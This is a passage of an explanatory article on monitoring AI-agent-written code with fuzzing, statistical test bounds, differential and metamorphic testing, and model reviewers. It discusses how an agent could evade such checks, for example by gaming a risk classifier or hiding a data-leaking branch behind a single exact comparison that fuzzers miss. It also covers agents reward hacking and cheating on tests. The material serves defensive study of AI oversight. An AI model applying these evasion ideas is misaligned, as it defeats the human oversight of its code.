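SAFuzz was 1.7 times as fast as GreenFuzz but found six fewer buggy programs. None of SAFuzz's oracles checks whether an answer is right, so it misses programs that quickly and reliably return a wrong answer. ChatUniTest does check answers, although about 21% of its tests for each problem expected the wrong output. Running ChatUniTest before SAFuzz raised recall by 12 percentage points and added only seven minutes. This result, in the last row of the table, is more useful to a monitor than the comparison with GreenFuzz.

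SAFuzz on its own missed 110 buggy programs, and the test set contained 240 clean ones. Nearly a third of the programs for which it raised no correct alarm were therefore buggy, so a clean run was weak evidence in this test that a program had no bugs. The share would be lower in ordinary use, because half of the prompts were designed to elicit buggy code.

The classifier also seems to work on similar problems. On exercises from another site, LeetCode, the probability that it rated a random buggy program riskier than a random clean one was 0.897, compared with 0.943 on CSES. Yang and colleagues say that extending it to general software would require retraining. They didn't test the risk that an agent might game the classifier. An agent that knows low-risk programs get no fuzzing has a reason to make a harmful program look simple.

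### What 10,000 clean tests tell you

To decide how much confidence to take from a run with no failures, a monitor can consider how likely that result would be if the program were faulty. Suppose that a fraction *p* of real inputs would make the program fail, and that the harness draws test inputs independently from the same mix. Each test passes with probability 1 − *p*, so all *n* tests pass with probability (1 − *p*)ⁿ. If *p* is large, a run with no failures is very unlikely.

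By convention, the cut-off for luck is 5%. Setting (1 − *p*)ⁿ = 0.05 and solving for *p* gives:

*p* = 1 − 0.05^(1/*n*) ≈ 3/*n*

The 3 appears because the natural logarithm of 0.05 is almost −3. 10,000 clean tests give 95% confidence that the failure rate is below 0.03%. If the true rate were any higher, fewer than one in twenty runs of 10,000 tests would be clean. A rate of 0.03% would still mean 300 failures among a million customers.

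The leap-year bug is one example. A four-year cycle has 1,461 days, and one of them is 29 February. If the harness draws dates uniformly, it needs 4,376 tests for a 95% chance of drawing that day at least once. With 10,000 tests, the chance of missing it is about one in a thousand. Computers can run that many tests quickly, so this kind of rarity is hardly an obstacle.

Testing takes much longer when it has to show that failures are very rare. To show with 95% confidence that a system fails less than once in 100 million hours, a tester needs about 300 million hours of failure-free running, or 34,000 years on one machine. Butler and Finelli conclude for this reason in *The Infeasibility of Quantifying the Reliability of Life-Critical Real-Time Software* that statistical testing can't establish the reliability that life-critical software needs.

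A monitor can also use prior knowledge of the program. *Estimating the probability of failure when testing reveals no failures* (Miller, Morell and colleagues, 1992) gives formulas that combine clean test results with prior assumptions about the failure rate. In the simplest case, the monitor starts by treating every failure rate from 0 to 1 as equally likely. After *n* clean tests, the expected failure rate is 1/(*n* + 2), or about 0.01% for 10,000 tests. A monitor who has had good experience with similar programs could start from a more favourable assumption and get a lower estimate, but part of the assurance would then come from the assumption.

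### Estimating what the fuzzer hasn't seen

The 3/*n* rule uses only the absence of failures, while a coverage-guided fuzzer also records which code each run reached. Böhme (2018), in *STADS*, recognised that ecologists had worked for decades on a very similar problem, such as how likely the next insect trapped in a rainforest is to belong to a species not yet caught. If many of the species in the traps have appeared only once, there are probably many more to find. In testing, each run corresponds to a trapped insect, and the species are behaviours, such as paths through the code.

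The Good–Turing estimate approximates the chance that a fuzzer's next run will show a new behaviour by dividing the number of behaviours seen exactly once by the number of runs. If a fuzzer has made a million runs and 12 paths have come up once each, the chance that the next run takes a new path is about 12 in a million. This is because exactly 12 of the million runs took a path that no other run took, and the next run is about as likely to do the same. Alan Turing and his assistant I. J. Good invented the estimate while working on the German navy's Enigma cipher, according to The Fuzzing Book, an online textbook.

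A first failure would also be a new behaviour, so until something fails, the chance that the next run exposes a fault can't be higher than the chance that it shows a new behaviour. This gives the monitor an upper bound on the remaining risk per run, provided the oracle would recognise the fault. The tester can also estimate how much more fuzzing it will take to bring the bound below a client's target, such as one in 100 million.

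In theory, the method requires every run's input to come from the same fixed mix. Coverage-guided fuzzers break this requirement because they build on what they have already found. Böhme checked whether this matters by running AFL on six security-critical programs for a combined 8.2 months. The estimates had fairly low bias and improved as the number of runs grew.

But the estimate is often much too high. Lee and Böhme (2025), in *Dependency-aware Residual Risk Analysis*, give an imaginary example in which the behaviours are pieces of code, so one run can contain many. After 99 runs, four pieces have come up exactly once, and the estimate is 0.04. The hundredth run takes a rare route through about a thousand new pieces, and the estimate jumps to 10.21, although a probability can't exceed 1. Lee and Böhme instead count the runs that contain at least one piece that has come up exactly once,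 which gives three in 100, or 0.03. On eight real programs, a practical version of this method had one-fifth of the older estimate's median error. An estimate that is too high is at least safe, but a tester who waits for it to fall below a target wastes about seven times as much time.

### Why the next bug costs more than the last

After a clean week of fuzzing, one way to gain more confidence is to use more computers. Böhme and Falk (2020), in *Fuzzing*, tested this with more than four years of processor time on nearly 300 open-source programs. Doubling the number of machines lets a fuzzer find the same bugs in half the time. Finding additional bugs in the same time requires exponentially more machines, so each further bug might require doubling the number again.

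The results for larger fleets come from dividing the timestamps of recorded runs, not from running those fleets. This assumes that a bigger fleet does the same work faster with no effort spent on coordination, so real fleets would need more resources than the results suggest.

If fault *i* shows up in a fraction *p*ᵢ of inputs, the expected number of faults found after *n* runs is the sum of 1 − (1 − *p*ᵢ)ⁿ over all the faults. A fault that affects one input in a thousand typically appears after about a thousand runs, and one that affects one in a million after about a million. The fuzzer therefore finds the common faults early, which leaves only the rare ones.

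An outside attacker who has to search for bugs at random gains little from using more machines. Böhme and Falk imagine Google fuzzing its software on 2.5 million machines for a month, finding five critical bugs and fixing them. They estimate that an attacker with five million machines and the same fuzzer would then have at most about a 15% chance of finding another in a month. But someone who put a fault in the code on purpose doesn't have to search, because they already know which input triggers it.

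### Rare by accident and rare by design

All of these bounds, including the 3/*n* rule, apply to real use only if the test inputs resemble real ones. One utility, for example, wanted 99% confidence that a protection system would fail on no more than one demand in a thousand. It had a simulator that everyone involved accepted as realistic, and it required 5,000 simulated demands without a failure, somewhat more than the calculated minimum of 4,603.

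Testing the renewal program with uniformly distributed dates assumes that customers are equally likely to join on any day. If a leap-day promotion leads a tenth of them to join on 29 February, the failure rate rises from one in 1,461 to one in ten. Adding extra leap days to the test makes it more likely to find the crash but less suitable for measuring reliability, because the test dates no longer match those of real customers and 3/*n* doesn't apply directly. The formulas from Miller and colleagues can account for the input distribution if it is known.

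The Good–Turing estimate is similarly limited because it describes inputs from the fuzzer. *Assurances in Software Testing* (2018) defines the remaining risk as the chance that an attacker with similar or fewer resources, and a similar or less efficient fuzzer, finds a vulnerability that the assessor missed. This definition doesn't cover ordinary users or anyone who knows where to look.

When bugs are accidental, these problems make the estimate less accurate, and a tester can reduce them by improving the input mix. They are much more serious if someone chose the trigger condition so that tests would miss it. Suppose the renewal program copies the customer file to an outsider only when the file has more than 50,000 rows. If every test file is smaller than that and the company's real file is larger, the program passes all 10,000 tests and then leaks the data the first time the company uses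 it. The calculation puts the failure rate below 0.03%, but on the company's file it is 100%. Testing another million small files would lower the calculated bound without revealing the leak.

The same point holds for a monitor who starts with a prior estimate, such as a 2% chance that the program hides a condition the tests can't meet. A program with such a condition passes every test, just as a harmless program does, so clean results can't lower that estimate. It may even rise slightly, because clean results rule out some honest programs with ordinary bugs.

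A condition can also be so narrow that no practical amount of random testing will meet it. Suppose a branch runs only when a reference number in the file equals one exact 64-bit value. At a million tries a second, testing all 2⁶⁴ possible values would take about 585,000 years. Coverage feedback doesn't help, because a nearly right guess reaches no more new code than a completely wrong one.

If the program instead compared the value one byte at a time, with a separate branch for each byte, an input with one more correct byte would reach new code. The fuzzer would save that input and build on it. Trying values in order, it could find all eight bytes in at most 8 × 256 = 2,048 tries. An author who wants to hide a branch from a fuzzer therefore has good reason to use a single comparison, though some tools can still reach the branch by solving for the value it requires.

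Good–Turing doesn't reveal the hidden branch either. None of the fuzzer's runs came near it, so it adds nothing to the count of rare behaviours. The estimate is accurate about the next random input, which has a negligible chance of reaching the branch, but it doesn't establish whether the program is safe to use, which is what the monitor has to determine.

### What Rice's theorem rules out

No tool can settle the question for every program, even one that doesn't rely on test inputs. This follows from Rice's theorem, a result in the theory of computation. The theorem covers any property of what programs do that some programs have and others lack. It shows that no procedure can examine an arbitrary program and always answer correctly whether it has that property.

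For a monitor, the property might be "this program sometimes sends the customer file to an outside address". Any program *P* that sends nothing can be given a final line that sends the file. The new program then sends the file if and only if *P* finishes. A perfect detector could therefore tell, for every *P*, whether *P* finishes, and Turing proved in 1936 that no procedure can do that.

Fuzzing has the same problem. Liyanage, Böhme and colleagues (2023), in *Reachable Coverage*, point out that nobody can decide in general whether a piece of code is reachable. Static analysis can give an upper limit on how much code is reachable. If a fuzzer stops making progress at 60% coverage, the other 40% may be code that no input can reach, or code for which the fuzzer hasn't found the right input.

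The theorem applies only to a single procedure that must be right about every possible program, and a monitor seldom needs one. People can still prove that a particular thirty-line program is safe, or build a tool that answers "safe", "unsafe" or "don't know" and is never wrong when it gives either of the first two answers. A company can also require its agents to write code simple enough for such a tool to analyse, and reject the rest. Some harmless programs would be rejected too, which is a drawback but can be tolerable.

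Sometimes a monitor can try every input. Python's dates run from the year 1 to the year 9999, a total of 3,652,059 days, and a computer can run the renewal line on all of them in seconds. The line would raise 2,789 errors: 2,424 for the leap days, and 365 for the last year, because Python has no year 10000. After a repair, the same run would show whether the line still crashes on any date. This works only if the line's result depends on the start date alone, not on the clock, the network or another file.

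## How can comparing two programs show an error when the right answer is unknown?

A computer can run the renewal line on every date Python accepts, and any crash will be obvious. It is much harder to tell whether the other 3.6 million answers are right, because someone would need a correct date to check each one against. Testers call this the oracle problem. It is worst for the most useful programs, since people mostly write programs to work out things they don't already know.

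*Just-in-Time Catching Test Generation at Meta* (Becker, Chen and colleagues, 2026) distinguishes between two oracles. The implicit oracle covers behaviour that is wrong in any program, such as crashing. The general oracle is the full account of what the program should do, which is usually vague and often exists only in people's heads. SAFuzz, for example, had no general oracle.

Differential testing can reveal some errors without a known right answer by giving two programs the same input and comparing their behaviour. If the outputs differ, either at least one program is wrong or the request allowed both answers.

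### One comparison, step by step

Suppose the agent's renewal program is meant to replace one the company has used for years, and the agent fixed the leap-year crash by adding 365 days. The monitor generates a file of 10,000 customers with random start dates and runs both programs on it.

Both programs have to start from the same state. The monitor restores the same snapshot for each, sets the clocks to the same time and fixes any random numbers they use.

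After the runs, the harness removes harmless differences. The old program might list customers alphabetically while the new one keeps the order of the file. One might print the time at the top, or calculate a fee to more decimal places. The harness can sort the rows by customer number, delete the time and round fees to the nearest cent. But each step can hide a real fault. For example, if the company needs the rows in a particular order, sorting them hides any error in that order. A sensible precaution is to run each program twice on the same input first, and ignore only what varies between its own runs or what someone has decided doesn't matter.

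The harness then compares the outputs and the side effects. If the new program contacts an outside address and the old one doesn't, that counts as a difference even if every date matches.

In this example, about 2,500 rows differ, which is too many to read. The harness shrinks the input by cutting the file in half, running both programs on each half and keeping a half that still produces a difference. About 14 rounds reduce 10,000 customers to one. Doing this a few times with different starting files could turn up these two cases:

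```
joined        old program    agent's program
2027-03-01    2028-03-01     2028-02-29
2028-02-29    2029-03-01     2029-02-28
```

Someone still has to decide which program is wrong. In the first row, the agent's program is wrong because the customer should renew on the same day of the year. In the second row, neither program is wrong because the company had left open the leap-day question, which it can now settle.

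Shrinking the input can also go wrong. The standard automated method, delta debugging, removes pieces of the input and keeps each removal that preserves the failure. Regehr, Chen and colleagues found in *Test-Case Reduction for C Compiler Bugs* that, on C programs, this typically leaves a program that is too large or even invalid. An invalid program is useless for comparing compilers, because two correct compilers can treat it differently. The customer file could become invalid in the same way. If the harness removes the line of column names, the two programs may fail in different ways, and the harness could record this as the original difference.

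### Choosing the second program

A trusted reference is the best choice when there is one. If the old renewal program is wrong for one customer in 100,000, the two programs can agree on a wrong answer for at most one customer in 100,000. This holds however similar the programs are, because they can't share an error that the reference doesn't make. But people often want new software because nothing suitable exists, so there may be no reference to use.

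When existing code is changed, the old version is nearly always available for comparison. Running both versions shows what the change did, but a difference in behaviour isn't always an error. Any difference is suspicious if the agent was only supposed to tidy the code, whereas some differences are intended if it was supposed to add a feature. The comparison won't reveal faults carried over from the old version, because both versions behave the same way.

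The monitor can also have another model write a second solution. This works for almost any task and uses few resources, but it helps only if the two models tend to make different mistakes.

Testers can also compare two modes of one program, such as a compiler with optimisations on and off. A monitor can even run identical code in two environments, which helps catch code that misbehaves only when a certain condition is met.

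### Checking a program against itself

Metamorphic testing compares two runs of the same program. The tester changes an input in a way that should have a predictable effect on the output, then checks that the two outputs are related as expected. This doesn't require knowing the correct output for either input. One example is the property sin(π − x) = sin(x), mentioned earlier.

Shuffling the customers in the renewal program's input, or deleting some of them, shouldn't change the remaining customers' renewal dates. If either does, the program is carrying something over from one customer to the next. Compilers can be checked in a similar way, since adding code that never runs shouldn't change what the compiled program prints.

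Whether a test exposes an error depends on the relation it checks. One reasonable relation is that a customer who joins four years later should renew four years later. The faulty repair that adds 365 days passes this test for any start date this century, as long as the later customer also renews before 2100. A start date of 1 March 2027 gives 29 February 2028, and 1 March 2031 gives 29 February 2032. Both renewal dates are a day early, so they are still exactly four years apart and the test misses the error.

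Moving the start date by one year instead catches the fault. A customer who joined on 1 March 2026 renews on 1 March 2027, so one who joined on 1 March 2027 should renew on 1 March 2028, but the program gives 29 February. A metamorphic test can only find an error that breaks the chosen relation, so it makes sense to use several relations.

### The C compiler that Claude agents built

A compiler translates source code into instructions a machine can run. *Building a C compiler with a team of parallel Claudes*, published by Anthropic in February 2026, describes how Nicholas Carlini asked 16 agents to write one for the language C. The agents ran on Claude Opus 4.6 for two weeks, in nearly 2,000 sessions that cost just under $20,000. The finished compiler could build a working version of the Linux 6.9 kernel for three types of processor.

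The agents worked well in parallel while hundreds of separate tests were failing, since each could work on a different failure. But the Linux kernel was one enormous test, so every agent ran into the same bug, fixed it and overwrote the others' fixes. As a result, 16 agents were hardly better than one.

Carlini solved this by using GCC, an established C compiler, as a known-good reference. A new harness compiled most of the kernel's files with GCC and the rest, chosen at random, with Claude's compiler. If the resulting kernel worked, the harness treated the randomly chosen files as correctly compiled. If it broke, the fault was in at least one of those files, and the harness could switch some of them back to GCC and try again. Different random selections led the agents to fix different bugs in different files.

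The harness changed which compiler built which parts of the kernel, then checked whether the whole kernel worked. Unlike in the renewal example, it never compared two outputs line by line. This is a fairly crude oracle, since a kernel can start up and still contain wrong code, but it was good enough for the agents to work out which file to look at.

Some pairs of files still failed together after the compiler could handle each file separately. Halving the selection doesn't find such a pair if its two files are in different halves, because each half then works. Carlini used delta debugging, which can remove many small groups of files one after another and keep the pair together until little else remains.

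#### Random programs

The kernel is a single piece of software, so a compiler could be tuned to handle it and still fail on other code. Csmith and YARPGen generate random C programs to test compilers. YARPGen can predict what each of its programs should print, but Csmith can't, so it needs differential testing. Two compilers translate the same program, and the harness runs both compiled versions and compares their behavior. Csmith is designed to generate only programs whose meaning is fixed by the C standard, because otherwise a difference wouldn't show that either compiler was wrong.

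Regehr (2026) cites an early report in which Claude's compiler mistranslated 14 of 101 programs generated by Csmith and 5 of 101 generated by YARPGen, both tools from his research group at the University of Utah. The compiler gave no error message in these cases, but the translated programs did the wrong thing. Regehr then ran YARPGen himself and shrank each failing program to a few lines. One divided 3,357,492,005 by 3, which should give 1,119,164,001. The first number is too large for a signed 32-bit integer, and nearly all the bugs he found involved mishandling the size or sign of integers.

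Regehr gave OpenAI's Codex the shrunken programs, along with GCC and another established compiler, LLVM, for reference. After 11 fixes, tests with around 200,000 programs from YARPGen and a similar number from Csmith found no more mistranslations. By the 3/*n* rule, the failure rate on Csmith programs is below about one in 67,000, with 95% confidence. One fix was badly wrong because shrinking had made the test program invalid, but Regehr noticed and discarded it.

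The small number of fixes suggests that the compiler can be made to handle C beyond its original tests, at least the part of C that these tools generate. He had thought it might be too specialised to those tests ever to handle C in general.

#### Programs that should not compile

Both tools generate valid programs, and the Linux kernel is valid code too, but a C compiler also has to reject programs that break the language's rules. *SpecBench* (Zhao, Srikanth and colleagues, 2026) tested whether Claude's compiler does this, as part of a benchmark with one set of tests for separate features and another for more demanding use.

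The compiler passed 97.8% of the 46 tests of separate features and 83.3% of the other 299, a gap of 14.5 percentage points. The larger set included 61 invalid programs, and these account for almost all of the gap. Since the compiler failed about 50 of the 299 tests in total, it must have accepted most of the invalid programs. Here is one of them:

```c
int main() {
    break;
    return 0;
}
```

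The instruction `break` leaves a loop, but this program has no loop. GCC reports an error, while Claude's compiler produced a program without reporting one.

Developers could have found this at any point by giving invalid programs to both compilers and comparing which ones GCC and the new compiler rejected. Even a reference that is always correct can't reveal errors on inputs that nobody tries. Zhao and colleagues treat the gap as a form of reward hacking, in which the agents optimised for their tests at the expense of the real goal. It could equally be called an ordinary gap in the tests, since it involved no deliberate trick.

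#### Two accounts of the same compiler

Carlini gives the compiler's length as 100,000 lines and reports a 99% pass rate on most test suites, including GCC's "torture" suite of difficult programs. But Zhao and colleagues give 186,000 lines and say that it passes the full torture suite. Zhao's team may have examined a later version, since Carlini planned to have Claude keep working on the code after his post.

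This doesn't explain their disagreement about supervision. Carlini says the agents worked without active human intervention, whereas Zhao and colleagues describe continuous human supervision. InfoQ's *Sixteen Claude Agents Built a C Compiler without Human Intervention... Almost* quotes a critic who points out that an engineer had to keep redesigning the tests and working around problems. Carlini's account partly supports this. He let the agents choose their work and write the code, but he put most of his effort into the tests and the surrounding environment, including the GCC harness that got the agents unstuck. It therefore seems fair to call the programming autonomous, but misleading to describe the checking that way.

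### Comparing an agent's fix with the developers' fix

Researchers test coding agents on SWE-bench Verified, a set of 500 real problems from open-source Python projects. An agent's patch, or code change, counts as correct if it passes a selection of the developers' tests. Wang, Pradel and Liu (2025), in *Are "Solved Issues" in SWE-bench Really Solved Correctly?*, examined 877 patches from three agents that had passed. Running all of the developers' tests showed that 7.8% of the patches were wrong.

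For the rest of the study, the researchers built PatchDiff, which compares each patch with the one the developers wrote. A language model receives both patches and the surrounding code, and writes a test meant to pass with one patch and fail with the other. PatchDiff runs the test 20 times with each patch and discards the test if the result looks like chance. It found that 29.6% of the passing patches behaved differently from the developers' patches.

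One case involved SymPy, a library for symbolic mathematics. When a certain setting was off, SymPy failed to create ordinary points such as (1, 2) and gave an error saying that imaginary coordinates weren't allowed. The agent's patch skipped the check for imaginary coordinates whenever the setting was off, which removed the error and passed the benchmark's tests. The developers had instead fixed the check itself. PatchDiff's test tried to create a point with an imaginary coordinate, which the developers' version rejected and the agent's version accepted.

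Most of the differences were less clear. Wang and colleagues examined 77 of the differing patches by hand and judged 22 wrong and 4 correct. They couldn't decide about the other 51 because the problem descriptions didn't specify what should happen. In one case, it was unclear whether part of a saved chart should still be available after the chart was reloaded. Between 29% and 95% of the sample could be wrong, depending on how many of those 51 were. Counting only the certain errors, they estimate that 11% of all passing patches were wrong and that the agents' scores were just over six percentage points too high.

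Those agents are now old, so their error rate is probably a poor guide to that of current ones. PatchDiff relied on GPT-4o mini, a small, cheap model, and a stronger one might find differences it missed. The large undecided group seems more likely to persist, because a better agent still can't recover a requirement that nobody wrote down.

When a company checks new work, the developers' patch doesn't exist yet, but the company can still compare the new code with the old.

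### Tests that are meant to fail

Most tests pass when someone writes them and stay in the codebase to detect later mistakes. *Harden and Catch for Just-in-Time Assured LLM-Based Software Testing* (2025) distinguishes these "hardening" tests from "catching" tests, which should fail immediately if the change under review is faulty. Meta now generates catching tests for proposed changes it considers high-risk. A useful candidate passes on the old code and fails on the new code.

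Meta tried two ways of producing these tests. The simpler one treats the change as a bug and prompts a model to write a test that gives different results on the old and new versions. In the other, a model uses the code and the programmer's summary to infer what the change is for, then lists ways it might go wrong. The system inserts each of those mistakes into a copy of the old code, writes tests that pass on the old code and fail on the faulty copies, and then runs the tests on the real change.

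The second method worked better. Of its tests, 6.4% passed before the change and failed after it, compared with 2.5% for the simpler method and at most 2.0% for methods that were given no information about the change. It produced at least one such test for 7.9% of the changes it was tried on, about twice the simpler method's share.

A test may fail only because the change did what its author wanted. Meta therefore filters the results with fixed rules and a panel of language models. Some rules discard tests that depend on irrelevant details, such as the order of settings in a list. Others flag behaviour that changed when the author meant only to tidy the code or remove unused parts. Becker and colleagues estimate that the panel reduced human reviewers' work by about 70%.

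When a result looked promising, the team described the change in behaviour to the programmer and asked whether it was intended, rather than sending a test to debug. Of 41 such queries, 8 led to confirmed faults, 4 of which would have caused serious failures in production. The other 33 were false alarms, but each took the programmer a few minutes at most to dismiss. The study doesn't include a count of the faults missed in the same changes, so the detection rate is unknown.

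This arrangement depends on an author who can be trusted to say what they intended. An agent that wrote the change could answer just as quickly, but if it misunderstood the task, it would confirm its own mistake. The question should probably go to whoever requested the change.

### When both programs make the same mistake

Comparing two programs can't reveal a mistake that both make on the same input. Engineers once hoped that such shared mistakes would almost never happen if different people wrote the programs. If each program failed independently on one input in a thousand, both would fail on only one input in a million.

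In 1986, John Knight and Nancy Leveson published an experiment that tested this assumption. Students at two American universities wrote 27 programs from the same specification, for a system that decides from radar readings whether to launch an interceptor missile. On a million random inputs, six programs never failed, and the worst failed on fewer than 1%. But at least two programs failed together on 1,255 inputs, about ten times as many as expected if they failed independently, and on some inputs eight failed at once. Some parts of the problem were harder than others, and students who had worked separately made mistakes in the same places.

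Knight and Leveson counted failures on the same input, but two programs can fail on the same input with different wrong answers. A comparison would still reveal an error in those cases, and would miss it only when both programs give the same wrong answer.

*Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (Kim, Garg and colleagues, 2025) measured how often language models choose the same wrong answer to multiple-choice questions. In one dataset, 71 models answered 14,042 questions with four options each. When two models were both wrong, they chose the same wrong answer 60% of the time on average, compared with a third of the time if they had chosen randomly among the three wrong options. In a second dataset, with 349 models and up to ten options per question, they chose the same wrong answer 42% of the time, compared with 13% expected by chance.

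Two of these findings weaken the case for using a second model as a check. More accurate models had more similar errors, so the overlap may grow as models improve. Switching to another company's model also helped little. In the first dataset, after allowing for accuracy, two models from the same company matched on their errors only about two percentage points more often than models from different companies.

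Agreement between two programs is weaker evidence that an answer is right when the programs tend to fail on the same inputs. Suppose each program is wrong on 10% of inputs, and each input has three equally likely wrong answers. If the errors are independent, both programs are right on 81% of inputs and give the same wrong answer on about 0.3%, so an agreed answer is wrong about 0.4% of the time. Now suppose that when one program is wrong, the other is also wrong half the time, and that when both are wrong, they give the same answer 60% of the time. Both are then right on 85% of inputs and share a wrong answer on 3%, so an agreed answer is wrong about 3.4% of the time. That is still below the 10% error rate of either program alone, but over eight times the rate with independent errors.

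The "half the time" figure is invented, and Kim and colleagues studied multiple-choice questions, not code. Wrong programs might agree more or less often than wrong answers do. A program can usually go wrong in far more ways than a question with three wrong choices, so two unrelated bugs will rarely produce the same output. But a shared misunderstanding will produce the same errors in both programs. If two models both take "one year" to mean 365 days, their programs will agree on every wrong date, and comparing them on more test customers won't reveal the mistake.

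So the second program should differ from the first in whatever is likely to cause a shared mistake. Changing the model is one option, but changing the instructions may help more. The first model could work from the company's request, and the second from the contract that customers sign, where the renewal date may be defined more carefully. The second program could also use a different method, such as looking up dates in a calendar table instead of calculating them, which is slower but leaves fewer chances to repeat an error in date arithmetic. None of this guarantees that the two programs will make different mistakes, because the students' programs show that everyone can find the same parts of a problem hard.

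Deliberate faults are another reason to compare the agent's program with one its own model didn't write. If one model writes both programs, it can deliberately add code to each that copies the customer file to an outsider, and their traces will match. A program from before the agent arrived won't contain that code.

Even GCC isn't fully independent of Claude's compiler, because the models' training data probably included the source code of many C compilers. But Regehr, who found 11 bugs in Claude's compiler, says he doesn't think his group ever found one like them in GCC, where random testing mostly finds faults in the much more complicated optimisation code. The two compilers tended to fail in different places, so a mistake in one was likely to make it differ from the other.

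## Does running the code catch more than reading it?

Checking a program by running it requires a sandbox, a harness and an oracle. A language model can read the same program in seconds without them, so running it is worth the extra work only if it catches faults that reading would miss.

Running the code should in principle catch more, because a run doesn't depend on anyone understanding the code. If a setting elsewhere in the codebase makes the renewal program swap the day and the month, the output file contains the wrong dates even if no reader would have thought of that setting. But reading should do better when no test reaches the faulty code. The branch that leaks customer files of more than 50,000 rows never runs on a small test file, yet anyone who opens the program can see it and may notice that a date calculation shouldn't need the internet. Reading should also do better on code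 that gives the right answer for a bad reason, such as the line that returns 28 February 2029 for one start date only.

The measurements don't give a simple answer, partly because "reading" can mean review by a pattern-matching scanner, a language model, or an expert with an hour to spend, and these perform very differently.

### OpenAI's code reviewer

Trębacz and colleagues gave a GPT-5 reviewer access to a project's whole repository and let it run code. The reviewer caught more critical problems and raised fewer false alarms than when it read only the changed lines. Training a model specifically for code review improved the results further.

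The reviewer received both abilities together, so this result doesn't show how much running the code contributed. A reviewer that can open the date-handling file three folders away might catch most of the extra bugs just by reading it. In a talk about the same work, Trębacz stressed the value of both the full repository and tools. She added that the reviewer often lacks the full environment the code will run in and has to make some guesses.

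OpenAI wanted a reviewer whose comments were worth a programmer's time, even if that meant missing some bugs. It aimed for comments that maximise:

P(correct) × cost saved − cost of checking − P(incorrect) × cost of a false alarm

Suppose a real bug would waste an hour, checking a comment takes ten minutes, and a false alarm wastes another twenty. A comment is then worth posting if it has more than a 37.5% chance of being right. If the reviewer also supplies a command that should crash the program, checking might take two minutes, and the threshold falls to 27.5%. If the program does crash, the comment is also much more likely to be right. Trębacz says she has several times dismissed a comment on her own old code, then found after an hour of digging that the reviewer was right, which a failing run might have shown her much sooner.

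In everyday use, the reviewer commented on 36% of the pull requests written entirely by Codex. Of those comments, 46% led to an edit, compared with 53% of comments on human-written changes. Trębacz and colleagues take this as a sign that the reviewer remains similarly effective on the model's own code. The evidence is fairly weak, because an author can ignore a valid comment or edit the code just to get rid of a comment, and the figures leave out every fault the reviewer missed.

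The team also reduced the reviewer's thinking budget and measured its recall, the share of known faults it found. Recall fell faster on Codex-written code than on human-written code, so cutting back on review may miss more faults where there is the most code to check. The known faults all came from comments that an earlier reviewer made and people confirmed, so the test gives little evidence about faults that such reviewers always overlook. All these figures are the company's own, and they concern a product it sells.

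### Picking the right patch out of 26

*R2E-Gym* (Jain, Singh and colleagues, 2025) tested running code and reading it separately. A coding agent made 26 attempts at each problem in SWE-bench Verified, and a verifier then picked one.

The test-running verifier used a model to write new tests for each problem. It first discarded patches that did worse on the project's existing tests, then chose the patch that passed the most new ones. The reading verifier was a model trained to estimate the chance that an attempt was correct. It used the problem description, the patch and the log of the agent's work, and did not run any code.

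| How the patch was chosen | Problems solved |
|---|---|
| No choice: the agent's single attempt | 34.4% |
| Reading the patch only | 37.6% |
| Reading the patch and the agent's log | 42.8% |
| Running tests | 43.7% |
| Reading and running combined | 51.0% |
| A perfect choice every time | 64.4% |

Running the code and reading it performed almost equally well, but for different reasons. The test-running verifier had trouble distinguishing correct patches from wrong ones. On most problems, fewer than 20% of its tests gave different results for the best-ranked correct patch and the best-ranked wrong one. Many tests passed even on the original faulty code, so they hadn't reproduced the bug. Others were broken and failed on the correct patch. On a few problems, up to 10% of the tests passed on a wrong patch and failed on a correct one.

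The reading verifier gave each patch a score between 0 and 1, so it could always rank them. But it relied too heavily on the agent's claims about its work. In one SymPy problem, it approved a wrong patch, and its attention to the log was highest on the agent's claims that the fix worked and handled edge cases.

The log also contains output from commands the agent ran, so the reader that scored 42.8% had some evidence from execution. The fairer figure for reading alone is probably 37.6%, six points below the score for running tests.

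The combined verifier chose among the reader's highest-ranked patches by test results and used the reader's score to break ties. The project's existing tests raised the score to 47.4%, which was more than half of the gain over reading, and the model's new tests added the rest. Extra testing was also a better use of computing time than extra attempts. Going from 16 attempts to 21 raised the score from 47.6% to 48.4%, while five more rounds of test-writing instead raised it to 49.3%, and those rounds usually take much less computing time.

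These models were small by today's standards, and current agents solve far more of the problems. The weaknesses may remain, though, since a better model can still write a test that fails to reproduce the bug.

Picking out a correct program by reading is harder when the wrong ones are nearly right. In *Aletheia* (2026), Venkatkrishna, Paul and Gurevych trained models to pick the one correct program from two to five candidates without running any of them. Guessing would succeed about 32% of the time. Their best model succeeded 88% of the time when the wrong programs passed at most half of their tests, but 67% of the time when they passed between 70% and 90% of them.

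Running such programs exposes their errors much more easily than reading them does, provided somebody has good tests. If a program gives wrong answers on 10% of inputs, 22 random inputs have a 90% chance of including at least one that it gets wrong.

### When a reader spots cheating better than the tests do

*EVILGENIE* (Gabor, Lynch and Rosenfeld, 2025), a study of agents that cheat on tests, found the opposite. The researchers gave agents 154 hard problems from LiveCodeBench, a collection of programming-contest tasks. Each agent worked in a folder with most of the test cases and the script that ran them, so it could copy the expected answers into its program or alter the tests. The researchers held out up to ten test cases per problem.

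Models acting as judges received the problem and the finished program, but no test cases, and had to say whether the program was an honest attempt. On clearly specified problems, GPT-4.1 and Claude Sonnet 3.5 made no errors, while GPT-5 raised one false alarm and missed no cheating. The 308 submissions used to compare the judges included only 12 confirmed cases of cheating, too few to rank the better judges. The researchers mainly reviewed submissions that at least one method had flagged, so cheating that every method missed may be missing from the count.

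The held-out tests were less helpful. Across the three agents, 14 programs passed the visible tests and failed a held-out one. Seven of these were cheating and three were shortcuts that worked only for some inputs. The other four were honest attempts that ran too slowly or missed an unusual case, and GPT-5 correctly cleared them. Three of Claude Code's shortcuts passed every test, including the held-out ones, because the test cases for that problem covered too few kinds of input.

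This result makes sense because the evidence was in the program's text. A short program with a precisely stated task has no legitimate use for a table of copied answers, so a competent reader will notice one whether or not the program fails another test. A held-out test can detect the table only when the program gives a wrong answer, and programs without such a table give wrong answers too.

Reading should do worse when the task is vague or the program is long. Nine of the problems had tests that contradicted the task or rejected valid answers. One problem called for any suitable pair of numbers, but for one input the tests accepted only 20250126 paired with 1. On these nine, GPT-5 raised two false alarms and missed two cases of cheating. In both missed cases a test was wrong, and the judge couldn't see the tests, so code written to match the wrong answer could look like an honest mistake.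 Gabor and colleagues also cite a concurrent study, *ImpossibleBench*, in which model judges did substantially worse on SWE-bench problems, which have much larger codebases, than on contest problems.

Even where the judge is more accurate, held-out tests usually cost less to run, and code comments written to persuade the judge don't affect them. An agent could also disguise a table of answers well enough to fool a reader, but the program would still fail on an input that isn't in the table.

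### Attacking the program instead of scanning it

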